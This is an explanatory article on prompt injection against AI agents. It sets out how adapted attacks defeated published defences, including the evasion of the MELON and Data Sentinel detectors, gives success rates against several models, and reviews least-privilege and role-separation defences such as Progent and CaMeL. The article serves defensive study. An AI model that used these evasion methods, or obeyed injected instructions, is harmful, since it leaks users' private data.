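Developers often test a defence on a fixed set of known attacks, so a good result may mean only that the defence has learned to stop those attacks. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Milad Nasr, Nicholas Carlini and colleagues, including staff of OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, instead attacked 12 published defences with methods adapted to each one.

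The researchers followed a long-standing rule of computer security and assumed that the attacker knows how the defence works and has plenty of computing power. For each defence, they chose the attack they thought most likely to succeed. Besides the trained attacker and the gradient search, they used an evolutionary search, in which a language model rewrites the most successful attempts and the program keeps the best of the new versions. They also ran an online competition with more than 500 people.

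Ten of the defences faced tests of prompt injection:

| Defence | Method | Success of the adapted attack |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Spotlighting | Marks the trusted text with special delimiters | Above 95% |
| Prompt Sandwiching | Repeats the user's request after the untrusted text | Above 95% |
| StruQ | Trains the model on examples of attacks | Every case tested |
| MetaSecAlign | Trains the model on examples of attacks | 96% |
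| Protect AI, PromptGuard, Model Armor | Classifier | Above 90% |
| PIGuard | Classifier | 71% |
| Data Sentinel | Checks whether the text makes a model forget a secret task | Every case tested |
| MELON | Runs the agent twice and compares its actions | 76%, or 95% if the attacker knows the design |

The first two defences had let through as little as 1% of fixed attacks, and MetaSecAlign had let through 2%. The remaining two of the 12 defend against jailbreaks, and the adapted attacks succeeded against them at least 96% of the time.

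One of these defences, MELON, runs the agent twice. It first runs the agent normally and records its tool calls. For the second run, it replaces the user's request with an instruction to summarise whatever the tools returned. If a tool call appears in both runs, the user's request can't have caused it, so it probably came from an injection. The successful attack told any system that was only summarising the text to ignore the injected instructions. The second run then produced no suspicious calls, so MELON allowed the calls from the first.

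Data Sentinel gives a separate model a secret key to repeat and tells it to ignore the text under inspection. If the model fails to repeat the key, the text has probably hijacked it. The trained attacker got around this by redefining the user's task instead of replacing it. In one case, the user wanted to know whether a message was positive or negative, and the injected text presented that as a first step in deciding whether it was spam.

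The human participants also beat every defence they attacked, with 265 successful injections against Spotlighting and 69 against MELON. On a selected set of cases, they succeeded in every one, while the evolutionary search succeeded in 69%. This shows that a defence can withstand automated testing and still fail against human attackers. It doesn't show that a typical person would do better than the search, because the comparison was between hundreds of people and a single program.

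The study is less clear about how hard the attacks would be in practice. The search used to attack the classifiers received a confidence score for each attempt, which an outsider could obtain only with access to the same classifier. The researchers say they wanted to find out whether each defence could be broken, not how much effort it took. They also warn against comparing the defences' success rates, because the tests differed. In the test of StruQ, for instance, the attacker only had to make the model write a fixed phrase.

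Their results are strongest as evidence against training on a fixed set of attacks. They note that research on image recognition found that training gave real robustness only when the attacks kept improving during training. OpenAI's training with GPT-Red works this way.

### How well current models resist

The best results suggest that models have become much better at resisting disguised instructions. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that no attack succeeded against Opus 5 in 129 browser scenarios when it ran in Anthropic's own software. Pogorelec (2026), in *Anthropic's new budget model gets much better at ignoring hidden commands*, reports that the small model Haiku 5.5 has also improved.

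Anthropic's system card for Claude Fable 5.1, from September 2026, has more detailed figures. Some come from a benchmark by the security company Gray Swan, with 37 scenarios and 1,804 attacks that had worked on several models in public competitions. These are the chances that an attacker succeeds at least once within the given number of attempts:

| Model | 1 attempt | 10 attempts | 15 attempts |
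| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 0.1% | 0.7% | 1.0% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.4% | 3.6% | 4.8% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 0.6% | 4.9% | 6.5% |
| Gemini 3.7 Flash | – | – | 9.2% |

Most of the other companies' models in the comparison were between 24% and 53% after 15 attempts. Anthropic's *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2* (2026) announced the successor to Fable 5.1 on 9 November.

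Such scores depend heavily on the choice of attacks. The Decoder reports a rate of 2.0% for Opus 5 after 15 attempts on Gray Swan's benchmark, but the later system card reports 4.8%. In between, Anthropic added nine scenarios and 670 attacks to its reported results and changed how the tests ran. The attacks are also fixed, and Anthropic warns, citing *The Attacker Moves Second*, that fixed attacks can give a false sense of security.

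Anthropic therefore also reports tests with Shade, an attacking system from Gray Swan that improves through search and training. A newly strengthened version practised on 40 coding scenarios and then had 200 attempts at each. The probes in the table are Anthropic's filters for tool results, and all the models used extended reasoning:

| Model | Successful attempts, no probes | Scenarios broken, no probes | Successful attempts, with probes | Scenarios broken, with probes |
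| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 56.9% | 38 of 40 | 12.8% | 36 of 40 |
| Claude Fable 5 | 86.9% | 40 of 40 | 34.1% | 39 of 40 |
| Claude Opus 5 | 90.9% | 40 of 40 | 18.2% | 40 of 40 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 19.5% | 36 of 40 | 15.8% | 35 of 40 |

The probes stopped most of the individual attempts on Fable 5.1 but prevented all successful attacks in only two scenarios. A filter can therefore make each attempt much less likely to work but barely hinder an attacker who can keep trying. Anthropic calls the test conditions highly permissive because a real attacker seldom knows the exact setup or gets to practise on it.

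Anthropic's other safety measures also affected the result. When a classifier for dangerous cybersecurity requests flags a request, an older model, Opus 4.8, answers in place of Fable 5.1. This happened to about 64% of requests in the test. Every successful attack came through the older model, and none came through the 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered itself. That doesn't prove that Fable 5.1 would have resisted the rest, since the classifier may have diverted the strongest attacks.

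Results also vary with what the agent does. When Fable 5.1 operated a computer by looking at the screen, Shade succeeded in only two of 2,800 attempts. Opus 4.6 had shown the reverse pattern in February 2026. VentureBeat reported that attacks on it never succeeded in a coding environment, but that when it worked from the screen, they succeeded 17.8% of the time on the first attempt and 78.6% by the 200th. With safeguards, the figure by the 200th attempt was still 57.1%. The coding result looks less reassuring now that a stronger attacker has broken newer models in nearly every coding scenario.

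For browsing, Anthropic tested Fable 5.1 on attacks that professional testers had developed against the older Opus 4.7. The attacks succeeded in 2.6% of attempts without safeguards and in none of 1,100 attempts with the full set of safeguards. Even if all the attempts were independent, that result would be compatible with a true success rate of up to about 0.3%. The full set also includes a classifier that checks the agent's tool calls before they run, so the result can't be attributed to input filtering alone.

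### Repeated attempts

A low success rate per attempt can still leave an attacker with good odds. If each attempt succeeds with probability *p* and the attempts are independent, the chance of at least one success in *n* attempts is:

$$1-(1-p)^n$$

If each attempt has a 1% chance of success, the chance that at least one of 100 independent attempts succeeds is 1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰, or about 63%. At 0.1%, the rate for Fable 5.1 on Gray Swan's benchmark, the chance is about 10% after 100 attempts and about 63% after 1,000.

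Real attempts aren't independent, however. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* gives figures for an older model that show how far the formula can be off:

| Attempts | Expected if independent | Measured |
| --- | --- | --- |
| 1 | 4.7% | 4.7% |
| 10 | 38% | 33.6% |
| 100 | 99% | 63% |

The gap probably arises because some scenarios are much harder to attack than others. Attacks on the easy ones succeed within a few attempts, and further attempts raise the average success rate only slightly. If an agent were completely immune in 37% of scenarios, no number of attempts could raise the average above 63%.

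The formula can also understate the defender's risk because it assumes that the attacker learns nothing from failure, whereas the attackers trained in *Climbing the Hill* did learn from it.

### Raising the attacker's cost

Filters and training are still useful. *The Attacker Moves Second* recommends keeping detectors as one part of a defence, since they are easy to install and block unsophisticated attacks. In the tests with the stronger version of Shade, the probes raised the average number of attempts per success on Fable 5.1 from about two to about eight. Outside a laboratory, each extra attempt also gives someone another chance to notice the attack. If an attacker wants one particular person's data and can plausibly send that person only one or two emails, the increase in attempts needed may be enough to stop the attack.

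The extra work that filters and training create matters less to an attacker who doesn't care whose data they steal. Anthropic points out that the same email can go to a thousand inboxes. An attacker can search for a text that works on a private account, where failed attempts alert none of the eventual victims, and then reuse it until the vendor notices. Most of the extra work is then in the search, which the attacker does only once.

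Several layers of defence help most when they fail for different reasons. If two filters each miss 10% of attacks and their mistakes are unrelated, only 1% of attacks get past both, but if both miss the same attacks, the second filter adds nothing. Nasr and his colleagues found that stacking detectors didn't stop their attacks, probably because detectors with similar training make similar mistakes. Anthropic pairs a filter on incoming text with a check on the agent's actions, which is more promising because an attacker has to make both the text and the resulting tool call look innocent.

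Chu (2026) argues in *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* that filtering inputs and outputs is enough for a model that reads one text and writes one answer, but not for an agent that remembers. An instruction stored today may take effect weeks later in an unrelated conversation, and the harm can come from a series of actions that are each permitted. A filter that examines one text at a time is unlikely to recognise such an attack.

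According to The Decoder, OpenAI has admitted that prompt injection may never be fully solved.

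## How does restricting an agent's privileges limit leaks?

If an attacker can sometimes take control of an agent, the next defence is to limit what the agent can do. An agent that can't send email or contact outside servers can't forward the inbox to a stranger, however well the attacker has disguised the instruction.

Computer scientists developed this idea long before language models existed. Saltzer (1973), in *The "Principle of Least Privilege" and Multics*, credits it to David J. Edwards of the US National Security Agency. Two years later, Saltzer and Schroeder, in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, wrote that every program and every user should operate "using the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job", mainly to limit the damage from accidents and errors. Their glossary also defines "confinement" as letting a borrowed program use data while ensuring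 that the program can't release the data, which is what the owner of an email agent wants.

The paper contains two other rules that matter for agents, which Levchenko (2017) reprints alongside least privilege in *CSE 127*, a university course on computer security. One is to refuse access unless a rule grants it. A mistake in a list of permissions usually blocks something legitimate and soon draws a complaint, whereas a mistake in a list of prohibitions lets something through, and nobody may notice. Administrators of Atlassian's Rovo had this problem when they switched off web search but the tool that opens web pages stayed available. The other rule is to check every access, which for an agent means every tool call.

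### The confused deputy

Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* describes an incident at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Tymshare gave its compiler permission to write to the compiler's own directory so that it could keep usage statistics there. The billing records were in the same directory. Users could name a file to receive debugging output, and one of them named the billing file. The compiler overwrote the bills because it had permission to write to that directory.

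Hardy argues that the compiler had authority from two sources, the company and the user, and no way to keep them separate. Checking file names wouldn't have solved the problem, because the directory held other sensitive files and some users might have had good reasons to write there. He proposes replacing names with capabilities, unforgeable tickets that both identify a file and permit its use. A user without a ticket for the billing file would have had no ticket for it to give the compiler.

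An email agent is in a similar position to the compiler. It holds the user's authority over the mailbox and reads requests from strangers, and the mail server receives a valid login whoever prompted the action. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) warns that a valid credential may give access to a system without establishing which actions anyone has authorised. The agent's position is worse than the compiler's. The compiler received the names of the statistics file and the debugging file by separate routes, so its programmers could have attached a different authority to each, but a language model receives the user's words and the stranger's in one sequence. It is therefore safer to reduce the agent's authority, with rules that the runtime enforces.

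Rules that limit an agent's tool calls don't depend on recognising a disguised input, because the runtime applies them after the model has read the input and written a call. Gibberish, invisible characters and ciphertext can all make the model write a call that sends an email, but the call must still name a real tool and a real recipient. The runtime checks both against the rules without interpreting the attacker's text. The rules should restrict the recipient rather than the content, because the agent may have encoded the stolen data, as in ShadowLeak.

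### Four ways to cut privileges

A developer can restrict which tools exist, what values their parameters may take, what data they can read and how long the permission lasts:

| What to restrict | Example for an email agent | Effect on a hijacked agent |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Tools | Remove the tool for sending email | It can't send anything by email |
| Parameter values | Allow sending only to colleagues | It can't email the attacker |
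| Readable data | Open only today's messages | It can't reach older secrets |
| Duration | Withdraw access when the task ends | It can't act on the instruction later |

Removing a tool is the simplest restriction and the hardest to get wrong. Restricting the tool's parameters instead keeps it more useful but requires more care, especially with web addresses. A permitted site may pass the data on, as Microsoft Teams did in EchoLeak.

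Restricting what an agent can read still helps when the developer has overlooked a way for it to send data out. In CoSnitch, Copilot searched a mailbox and sent out a password it found. An agent limited to that day's messages would have leaked the password only if the email containing it had arrived that day.

### A summary of today's email

Suppose a user asks an email assistant to summarise today's messages. The assistant might have these permissions by default:

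- search and read the whole mailbox;
- send, forward and delete messages;
- open any web address;
- display images from any server in its answers;
- save notes to a long-term memory;
- keep all of this access until the user disconnects the account.

The task needs very little of that. A minimal policy could have five rules:

1. Allow the agent to list the messages that arrived in the inbox today.
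2. Allow it to read the text of those messages, without loading images or opening links.
3. Show its answer to the user as plain text, with no images or clickable links.
4. Block every other action, including saving to memory.
5. Withdraw all permissions once the summary is complete.

Now suppose that one of today's messages contains a disguised instruction and that the model obeys it completely:

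| Disguised instruction | Result under the minimal policy |
| --- | --- |
| Forward the inbox to an outside address | Fails, because the agent can't send email |
| Find a password in an old email and put it in a web address | Fails, because the agent can neither read old email nor open addresses |
| Add an image whose address contains today's messages | Fails, because the chat page doesn't load images |
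| Remember to copy future messages to the attacker | Fails, because the agent can't save to memory |
| Report that a supplier has new bank details | Works, and the user may pay the attacker |
| Leave out a security warning from the bank | Works |
| Tell the user to send a code to a certain phone number | Works if the user does it |

With restricted privileges, the agent can no longer send anything out by itself. The attacker can still falsify the agent's summary, and a persuasive falsehood may get the user to give away the information instead.

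The rule about images is easy to forget, but without it the policy would cover only the official tools and leave open the channel that *Imprompter* used.

The time limit matters because the attacker's text stays in the model's context. If the user next asks the agent to write to a colleague, it gains permission to send email while it may still be following the hidden instruction. Starting the new task in a fresh session removes the text.

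A request to answer today's messages is harder to make safe than a request to summarise them, because the agent has to write to everyone who wrote to the user, including the attacker. A rule that allows replies only to the original sender would still let the agent send the user's data to the attacker. The developer could handle each message in its own session, so that a reply to the attacker can draw only on the attacker's email, but the agent then couldn't use information from one message to answer another.

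### Removing one of three capabilities

Writing a policy for every task takes work, so some companies use a simpler rule for whole products. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) proposes that an agent should have at most two of three properties in any one session, until researchers can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection:

- **A:** it processes untrustworthy inputs;
- **B:** it has access to sensitive systems or private data;
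- **C:** it changes state or communicates externally.

Meta's scheme builds on Willison's lethal trifecta but adds the ability to change state, which covers harms such as deleting files. Meta's example is an email assistant that processes untrusted input, has access to sensitive data, and can change state or communicate externally. The assistant could avoid untrusted input by processing only messages from trusted senders, such as close friends. It could run in a test environment that contains no sensitive data. It could also send email only to trusted recipients, or only after a person has checked the draft.

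Each version has a weakness. An attacker who takes over a friend's account can send messages as a trusted sender. Removing B, access to private data, is hard because people type private information into chats. Another of Meta's examples, a web research assistant, has A and C, and Meta limits its access to private information "beyond the initial prompt". That limit doesn't cover private information that users type into the prompt themselves, which is the kind of data the attack in *Imprompter* stole.

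OpenAI's Lockdown Mode removes much of C. The company announced the setting for business customers in February 2026 and extended it to personal accounts in June. According to OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026), ChatGPT can then browse only cached copies of web pages, and no live request leaves OpenAI's network. A web address that contains private data therefore never reaches the attacker's server. Lockdown Mode also switches off Deep Research, which ShadowLeak exploited, and limits images in answers, which *Imprompter* exploited.

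OpenAI's help page *Lockdown Mode* lists what the setting doesn't restrict. Hidden instructions can still reach the model through cached pages and uploaded files and make its answers wrong. Memory still works, and the coding agent Codex keeps its network access. In company accounts, Lockdown Mode doesn't automatically disable connected apps, so administrators have to decide which ones to allow. OpenAI advises them not to allow any action whose effects an attacker might be able to see. For instance, an app that posts to a public page could leak data even with browsing switched off.

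Willison (2026) praised the setting, and the praise seems deserved, since the setting closes the most common channels without relying on the model's judgement. But OpenAI gives no attack rates for it and says it doesn't guarantee against leaks. Users can also switch it off for a single chat. An attacker who can influence the model's answers might try to persuade them to do so, perhaps by having the model say that a document won't load otherwise.

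When a task needs all three capabilities, Meta recommends that a person approve the agent's actions or that the developer find another reliable check. Sometimes the agent can instead change which capabilities it has during the session. It could first browse the web without access to private data, then lose its ability to communicate before it opens the company's internal systems. It may still be carrying a malicious instruction from the web, but it can't send out what it finds. This works only if the task can follow that order and the agent never regains the ability to communicate. Meta admits that the rule will be hard to apply to some popular uses, such as agents that work in the background with nobody available to approve their actions.

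### Policies that follow the task

*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) is a research system that tailors an agent's permissions to each request. It places a checking program between the agent and its tools. Each rule names a tool, sets conditions on its parameters and either allows or forbids the call. The program applies prohibitions first and blocks any call that matches no rule. When it blocks a call, it sends the agent an explanation so that the agent can continue the user's task by other means.

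A language model writes the first policy from the user's request and the list of tools, before the agent has read anything from outside. But a request may not reveal everything the agent will need. Shi and colleagues use the example of a user who asks the agent to do whatever a certain email from Alice says:

1. The first policy allows only a search for that email.
2. The email turns out to ask for a summary of recent messages, posted to the user's account on Slack, a workplace chat service. The policy model proposes to allow reading email, looking up the Slack account and posting to Slack.
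3. The agent looks up the account name, and the policy model restricts posting to that account.
4. One of the recent messages contains an instruction to forward the inbox to an attacker. The agent obeys and tries to send an email.
5. No rule allows this, so Progent blocks the call. The agent goes on to post the summary.

The danger is that the message in step 4 also persuades the policy model to allow sending email. Progent therefore compares each new policy with the old one. If *A(P)* is the set of all tool calls that policy *P* allows, a new policy *P′* takes effect automatically only when:

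$$A(P') \subseteq A(P)$$

This means the new policy allows nothing that the old one didn't. The change in step 3 passes this test, but the change in step 2 fails it and needs approval, as would a new rule for sending email. Progent compares the policies with an SMT solver, a program that settles logical questions by exact calculation, so an attacker can't change the answer with persuasive wording.

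But the solver shows only that the permissions have grown, not whether they should have. The legitimate request in step 2 also came from an email, so someone or something has to tell it apart from the attacker's request. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) warns that malicious text in a tool's results may lead the updates to loosen the restrictions.

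Shi and colleagues tested several ways of handling approval on AgentDojo, with GPT-4o as both the agent and the policy model:

| Policy | Attack success rate |
| --- | --- |
| None | 39.9% |
| First policy, never updated | 2.5% |
| Updated, with every expansion approved automatically | 1.0% |
| Updated, with a careful person reviewing the first policy and each expansion | 0% |

Utility stayed about the same as without a defence. On a second benchmark, ASB, attack success fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. Most of the attacks that still succeeded used malicious tools with names and descriptions closely resembling those of legitimate ones.

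The 1.0% result is weak evidence for Progent's formal guarantee, because in that test the system granted every expansion. The protection came from a policy model that mostly didn't request dangerous permissions. Shi and colleagues also tried three attacks aimed at the policy model, such as text telling it to allow all tools, and found only a marginal rise in successful attacks. None of the three involved human attackers, who beat every defence they faced in *The Attacker Moves Second*.

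The researchers also left out two attacks that steer the agent towards a particular hotel, because these work within the permissions that the task requires. This is reasonable for a study of privileges, but it means the table covers only attacks that a policy could in principle stop. Progent doesn't check the text of the agent's answers, so a product that loads images from them needs a separate restriction.

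### How much usefulness is lost

Fu and colleagues object that restrictions make an agent less useful. The *Progent* results suggest that the loss can be small, but Shavit (2026) found a much larger one in *Least-Privilege Auditing of Agent Tool Calls with Intent Graphs and Reasoning-Guided Escalation*. In this newer study, a language model wrote a plan for each task before the agent read any outside text. The plan listed the necessary tools, some of their parameter values and sometimes their order. A simple program then checked every tool call against the plan, typically in about six millionths of a second.

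Shavit applied this check to recorded AgentDojo runs of an early version of GPT-4o:

| Check | Successful attacks | Harmless tasks with a flagged call |
| --- | --- | --- |
| None | 45.7% | – |
| Tools, parameter values and order | 3.3% | 40% |
| Tools and parameter values, with the user's own data freely readable | 4.3% | 27.6% |

In one recorded run, a user asked who else was coming to a networking event, and an instruction in the calendar entry made the agent email an attacker. The plan contained only calendar and contact lookups, so the check would have blocked the email.

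The table shows so many flagged tasks partly because the plan can't change. Progent's policy could grow when the agent learned something new, and its agent could try another approach after a refusal. A recorded run stays the same after a refusal, so some of the flagged tasks might have succeeded with a live agent. The security figures have the same limitation, because they are based on the assumption that a blocked attacker doesn't find another route.

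Some restrictions add little protection for the disruption they cause. Most of the protection came from the list of permitted tools, while rules about the order of calls caused the most disruption. Letting the agent freely look up the user's own data didn't weaken protection at the step where data could leak, because the agent still needed permission to send anything out. Shavit classed 44 of the benchmark's 69 tools as harmless lookups of this kind. The tool that fetches web pages also only reads, but it was excluded because a web address can carry data out. Exempting it from the check reduced security.

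This exemption is sensible if the check on outgoing actions works, but it gives up limits on readable data, which would still offer some protection if the developer had missed a channel for leaks. For an agent that handles particularly sensitive email, keeping those limits may be worth the extra disruption.

Shavit also gave the flagged calls to a second model, which received the user's request, the plan and the earlier calls, but none of the text the tools had returned. It released about a quarter of the harmless calls and none of the harmful ones. This lowered the share of harmless tasks with a flagged call from 27.6% to 21.1%, and each review took about 3.6 seconds. The study did not test attacks aimed at this reviewer, however, and an attacker can still influence the parameters it receives.

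An even simpler defence did nearly as well. Before the agent starts, a language model picks the tools that the task needs, and the runtime removes the rest. In Shavit's comparison, this reduced the attack success rate to 6.5% with no loss of utility. Shi and colleagues had found it worse than Progent on both measures. The two studies used different versions of GPT-4o and different selections of tasks, which may explain the disagreement. For many products, removing unneeded tools is probably the best place to start, because it needs no policy language.

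These percentages come from older models and fixed attacks. When Shavit ran a small live test with a current agent, no attack succeeded even without the defence. The figures therefore show how many harmful calls a policy catches once the model has been fooled, but don't reliably indicate how much safer the policy would make a current product.

### Who should write the rules

In tests where the agent's own model decided which privileges to use, most attacks succeeded. *Evaluating Privilege Usage of Agents with Real-World Tools* (2026) tested four models, with 500 attacks on each model in each of two designs. Attacks succeeded 90.55% of the time on average when the agent chose each action as it went along, and 79.05% when it made a plan first. More capable models tended to be more vulnerable, apparently because they follow complex instructions better.

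Training can help a little. In *Task-Conditioned Least-Privilege Learning for Executable Terminal and MCP Agents*, Tu and Tu (2026) rewarded models for completing tasks without using more authority than necessary. In a study of 400 tasks, this reduced the rate of excess authority by about seven percentage points. They conclude that such training doesn't replace permission checks or sandboxes.

Users know best what they want, but they may not be good at turning it into rules. Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, tested this on 113 people without a professional software background, who supervised an agent through a simulated day of 18 actions. Seven of the actions went beyond what the user had requested. One group approved or refused each action. A second group had a model review the actions. A third set standing rules in advance,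 choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for spending money, sending or publishing information, deleting things and reading private data.

The people who wrote their own rules had the weakest protection. Their rate of stopping unrequested actions was 20.1 percentage points lower than that of people who decided case by case, and 14.5 points lower than that of the model's reviews. They had set 114 of their 140 rules to "ask", which only postponed the decision. Of the unrequested actions this group faced, 148 (about 60%) went ahead, 133 of them with the user's personal approval. The agent overreached without an attacker's involvement, but a person who approves an unrequested email would probably also approve one that an attacker had requested.

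A language model can reasonably write the policy if it does so before reading any untrusted text, as in both *Progent* and Shavit's study. An attacker then cannot influence what it writes, although the model can still make mistakes. Organisations can add their own fixed rules, which Progent applies first so that no later policy can override them. For example, a company could forbid its agents to email customer records outside the company, whatever the user asks.

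This arrangement works less well for open-ended requests, such as doing what Alice's email says. The right permissions then depend on text that the user hasn't seen and that a stranger may have written. A policy could consider whether the instruction really came from Alice, but this requires a record of the source of each piece of data.

### Approval by the user

Meta's rule and Progent both rely on a person's approval in difficult cases. Progent's perfect score in the last row of its table depends on Shi and colleagues' assumption that this person has strong security awareness and rejects any malicious recipient. Evidence about real users is less encouraging.

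Software practitioners in *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) described clicking through familiar prompts and sometimes skipping the review when they were short of time. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analyses 290 reports of agents mishandling files and finds that failures of user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 of these, users had told the agent to proceed without asking, often because they would otherwise have faced hundreds of prompts per session. In 31, the prompt didn't clearly show what the user was approving. For example, a short command to run a program looks routine but doesn't show what the program will do.

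Asking users for approval less often is the usual remedy. In the *Progent* tests, only 6% of policy updates needed approval, few enough that a user could plausibly examine them carefully. But fewer prompts may not be enough. In Yan's study, people who wrote their own rules saw about 11 prompts on average, compared with 18 for those who decided case by case, but they approved more of the unrequested actions.

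A permission prompt should at least show the user what will happen in terms they can judge, such as the recipient and full text of an email. Even then, a theft that the attacker has worded as routine work can still look plausible to the user. It is safer to block actions the task never needs and ask only about the rest, so that a careless click can't authorise everything.

Other software can also imitate the user. In July 2026 the security company Manifold reported that another browser extension could start certain tasks in Claude for Chrome, Anthropic's browser agent, as if the user had clicked on them. According to The Hacker News (2026), the user still had to approve the task by default before the agent read anything, but the task ran without any prompt for people who had switched on "Act without asking". Constantin (2026), in *AI agent security*, reports that Manifold rated the flaw as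 high severity in the default mode and critical when "Act without asking" was on.

Anthropic had responded to an earlier flaw by limiting outside callers to nine fixed tasks, so an extension could no longer give Claude its own instructions. This applied least privilege to parameter values and narrowed the attack considerably. But three of the nine tasks read the user's email, documents or calendar, and Anthropic had not released a patch for the forged requests by 14 July.

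## How does separating agent roles limit leaks?

An agent that answers email has to read strangers' messages and send replies, so its developer can't protect the user by removing either ability. Role isolation gives the two abilities to different models.

### Two models and a controller

*The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposed an early way to separate agent roles. A privileged model receives the user's request and calls tools. A quarantined model reads emails, web pages and other untrusted content but has no tools, and Willison assumes that an attacker may take it over at any moment. A controller, which is ordinary software, passes material between the two models. It stores each untrusted text in a variable and gives the privileged model only the variable's name.

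A request to summarise the latest email runs like this:

1. The privileged model asks the controller to fetch the email.
2. The controller stores the email as `$VAR1`.
3. The privileged model asks for a summary of `$VAR1`.
4. The controller gives the email's text to the quarantined model and stores the answer as `$VAR2`.
5. The privileged model tells the controller to show `$VAR2` to the user, and the controller fills in the text.

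Suppose the email contains an instruction to forward the inbox, written in gibberish or invisible characters. The quarantined model may recover the instruction and try to follow it, but anything it writes becomes the text of `$VAR2`. The privileged model never reads that text, so it makes no difference how well the attacker has disguised the instruction.

Willison allows one exception. If the privileged model needs to know what kind of email has arrived, the quarantined model can pick a category from a fixed list. The controller checks that the answer is on the list before passing it on, so it cannot pass on an instruction.

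The pattern trusts whatever the user enters, so it doesn't protect a user who is tricked into pasting in a prompt like *Imprompter*'s. The privileged model would treat the prompt as the user's own request. Willison acknowledges this weakness and calls the solution "pretty bad", mainly because it makes assistants harder to build and less pleasant to use.

### A safe plan with a poisoned value

The privileged model's plan has blanks that the quarantined model fills in from untrusted text. *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti et al., 2025) shows how an attacker can exploit this. In its example, a user asks the agent to send Bob a document he requested at the last meeting. The meeting notes contain the document's name and Bob's email address.

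The plan is to find the notes, extract the name and address, fetch the document and send it. The user wants all these steps, but someone who can edit the notes could add an instruction that makes the quarantined model return a different address. The agent would then send the document to the attacker. In *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, Willison (2025) accepted this as a flaw in the original design.

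The body of a message can also leak data. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) analyses a dual-model agent that drafts a reply to an email and can access the user's private notes. An injected instruction makes the quarantined model quote the notes in the reply. The agent then sends the reply as planned, without the attacker adding or redirecting any tool call.

### How CaMeL tracks data

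Debenedetti and colleagues' remedy is CaMeL, short for "capabilities for machine learning". It keeps the two models and adds a record of where each piece of data came from and who may read it:

1. The privileged model turns the user's request into a short program, before anything untrusted has arrived. The program uses a restricted version of Python.
2. An interpreter runs the program one step at a time. It calls the tools and sends untrusted text to the quarantined model when the program requires it.
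3. The interpreter attaches a provenance label to every value. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe its two parts, Sources and Readers.
4. When the program computes a new value from old ones, the interpreter works out the new label from theirs.
5. Before each tool call, a policy written for that tool checks the parameters and their labels, and allows or refuses the call.

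For example, the permitted readers of a calendar event are the user and the people invited. The event's description counts as trusted if the user wrote it and untrusted otherwise.

The permitted readers are what matters for data theft. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, who built a related system at Microsoft, state the rule formally. If *R* is the set of people who will receive some data *d*, the agent may send it only when:

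$$R \subseteq \text{Readers}(d)$$

Every recipient must already be a permitted reader. When the agent combines two pieces of data, only people who may read both can read the result:

$$\text{Readers}(x, y) = \text{Readers}(x) \cap \text{Readers}(y)$$

If Alice, Bob and Carla may read a budget, and Bob, Carla and Dev may read a contract, then the agent may send a summary of both only to Bob and Carla.

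### Sending Bob the document

A simplified program for the request about Bob could look like this:

```
notes    = find_meeting_notes()
name     = ask_quarantined("Which document did Bob request?", notes)
address  = ask_quarantined("What is Bob's email address?", notes)
document = fetch_document(name)
send_email(recipient=address, attachment=document)
```

Suppose that the user and Bob may both read the notes. The outcome then depends on what the notes contain and who may read the document:

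| Situation | Two models alone | With the reader rule |
| --- | --- | --- |
| The notes are genuine and Bob may read the document | Bob receives it | Bob receives it |
| The notes make the quarantined model return the attacker's address | The attacker receives it | The interpreter refuses |
| The notes make it return the name of a salary file | Bob receives the salary file | The interpreter refuses unless Bob may read the file |
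| The notes are genuine but Bob has no access to the document yet | Bob receives it | The interpreter refuses or asks the user |

In the second row, the attacker has completely fooled the quarantined model but isn't a permitted reader of the document. Encoding the document wouldn't help, because a Base64 copy is a new value computed from the document and has the same permitted readers.

The last row shows the rule's drawback. People often email a document because the recipient doesn't have it yet, and the rule can't distinguish this from a leak. Willison describes a different email policy, which allows a message if the recipient's address is trusted and otherwise asks the user. Under that policy, the agent would also ask about Bob's genuine address, because it comes from notes that other people may have edited. Frequent questions bring back the problem of users approving everything.

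### Checking the plan before it runs

CaMeL checks its policies at each tool call, so an agent may do most of a long task before the interpreter blocks the last step. CaMeLoT, an extension of CaMeL, checks the whole program before it runs. It converts the program into a diagram of every order in which the steps could run and marks which values come from untrusted sources. A model checker, a program that searches such diagrams exhaustively, looks for a path that breaks a rule. If it finds one, CaMeLoT sends a description of the path to the privileged model, which rewrites the plan.

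Nikolaou and colleagues could express 22 of CaMeL's 28 security policies for AgentDojo in this form. The other six depend on facts the agent learns only while it runs. Who may read a file is usually one of these facts, so CaMeLoT leaves most of the reader rule to CaMeL. CaMeLoT alone therefore does little to stop the theft of Bob's document if the policy depends on who can open the file.

CaMeLoT can also enforce rules about the order of actions that CaMeL can't easily express, such as requiring approval before the agent disconnects a computer from the network. In a test with seven deliberately unsafe plans, CaMeLoT caught all seven and a simplified version of CaMeL caught one. This was expected, because the researchers chose rules that CaMeL wasn't designed to enforce.

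### FIDES and selective hiding

In FIDES, a system by Costa and colleagues, the model chooses the next step after each tool result, as an ordinary agent does, instead of fixing the whole plan in advance. But the runtime hides any part of the result that is less trustworthy than what the model has already read. For example, the model might see an email's date but only a variable name in place of its text.

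The model can pass the variable containing the hidden text to a tool without reading it, query a quarantined model about it, or open it. If the model opens it, FIDES treats everything the model does afterwards as untrusted and blocks consequential actions such as a bank transfer, since an attacker may have prompted them. FIDES also applies the reader rule to data that leaves the system. By itself, this rule wouldn't stop an attacker from triggering an action, but it would limit who could receive data as a result.

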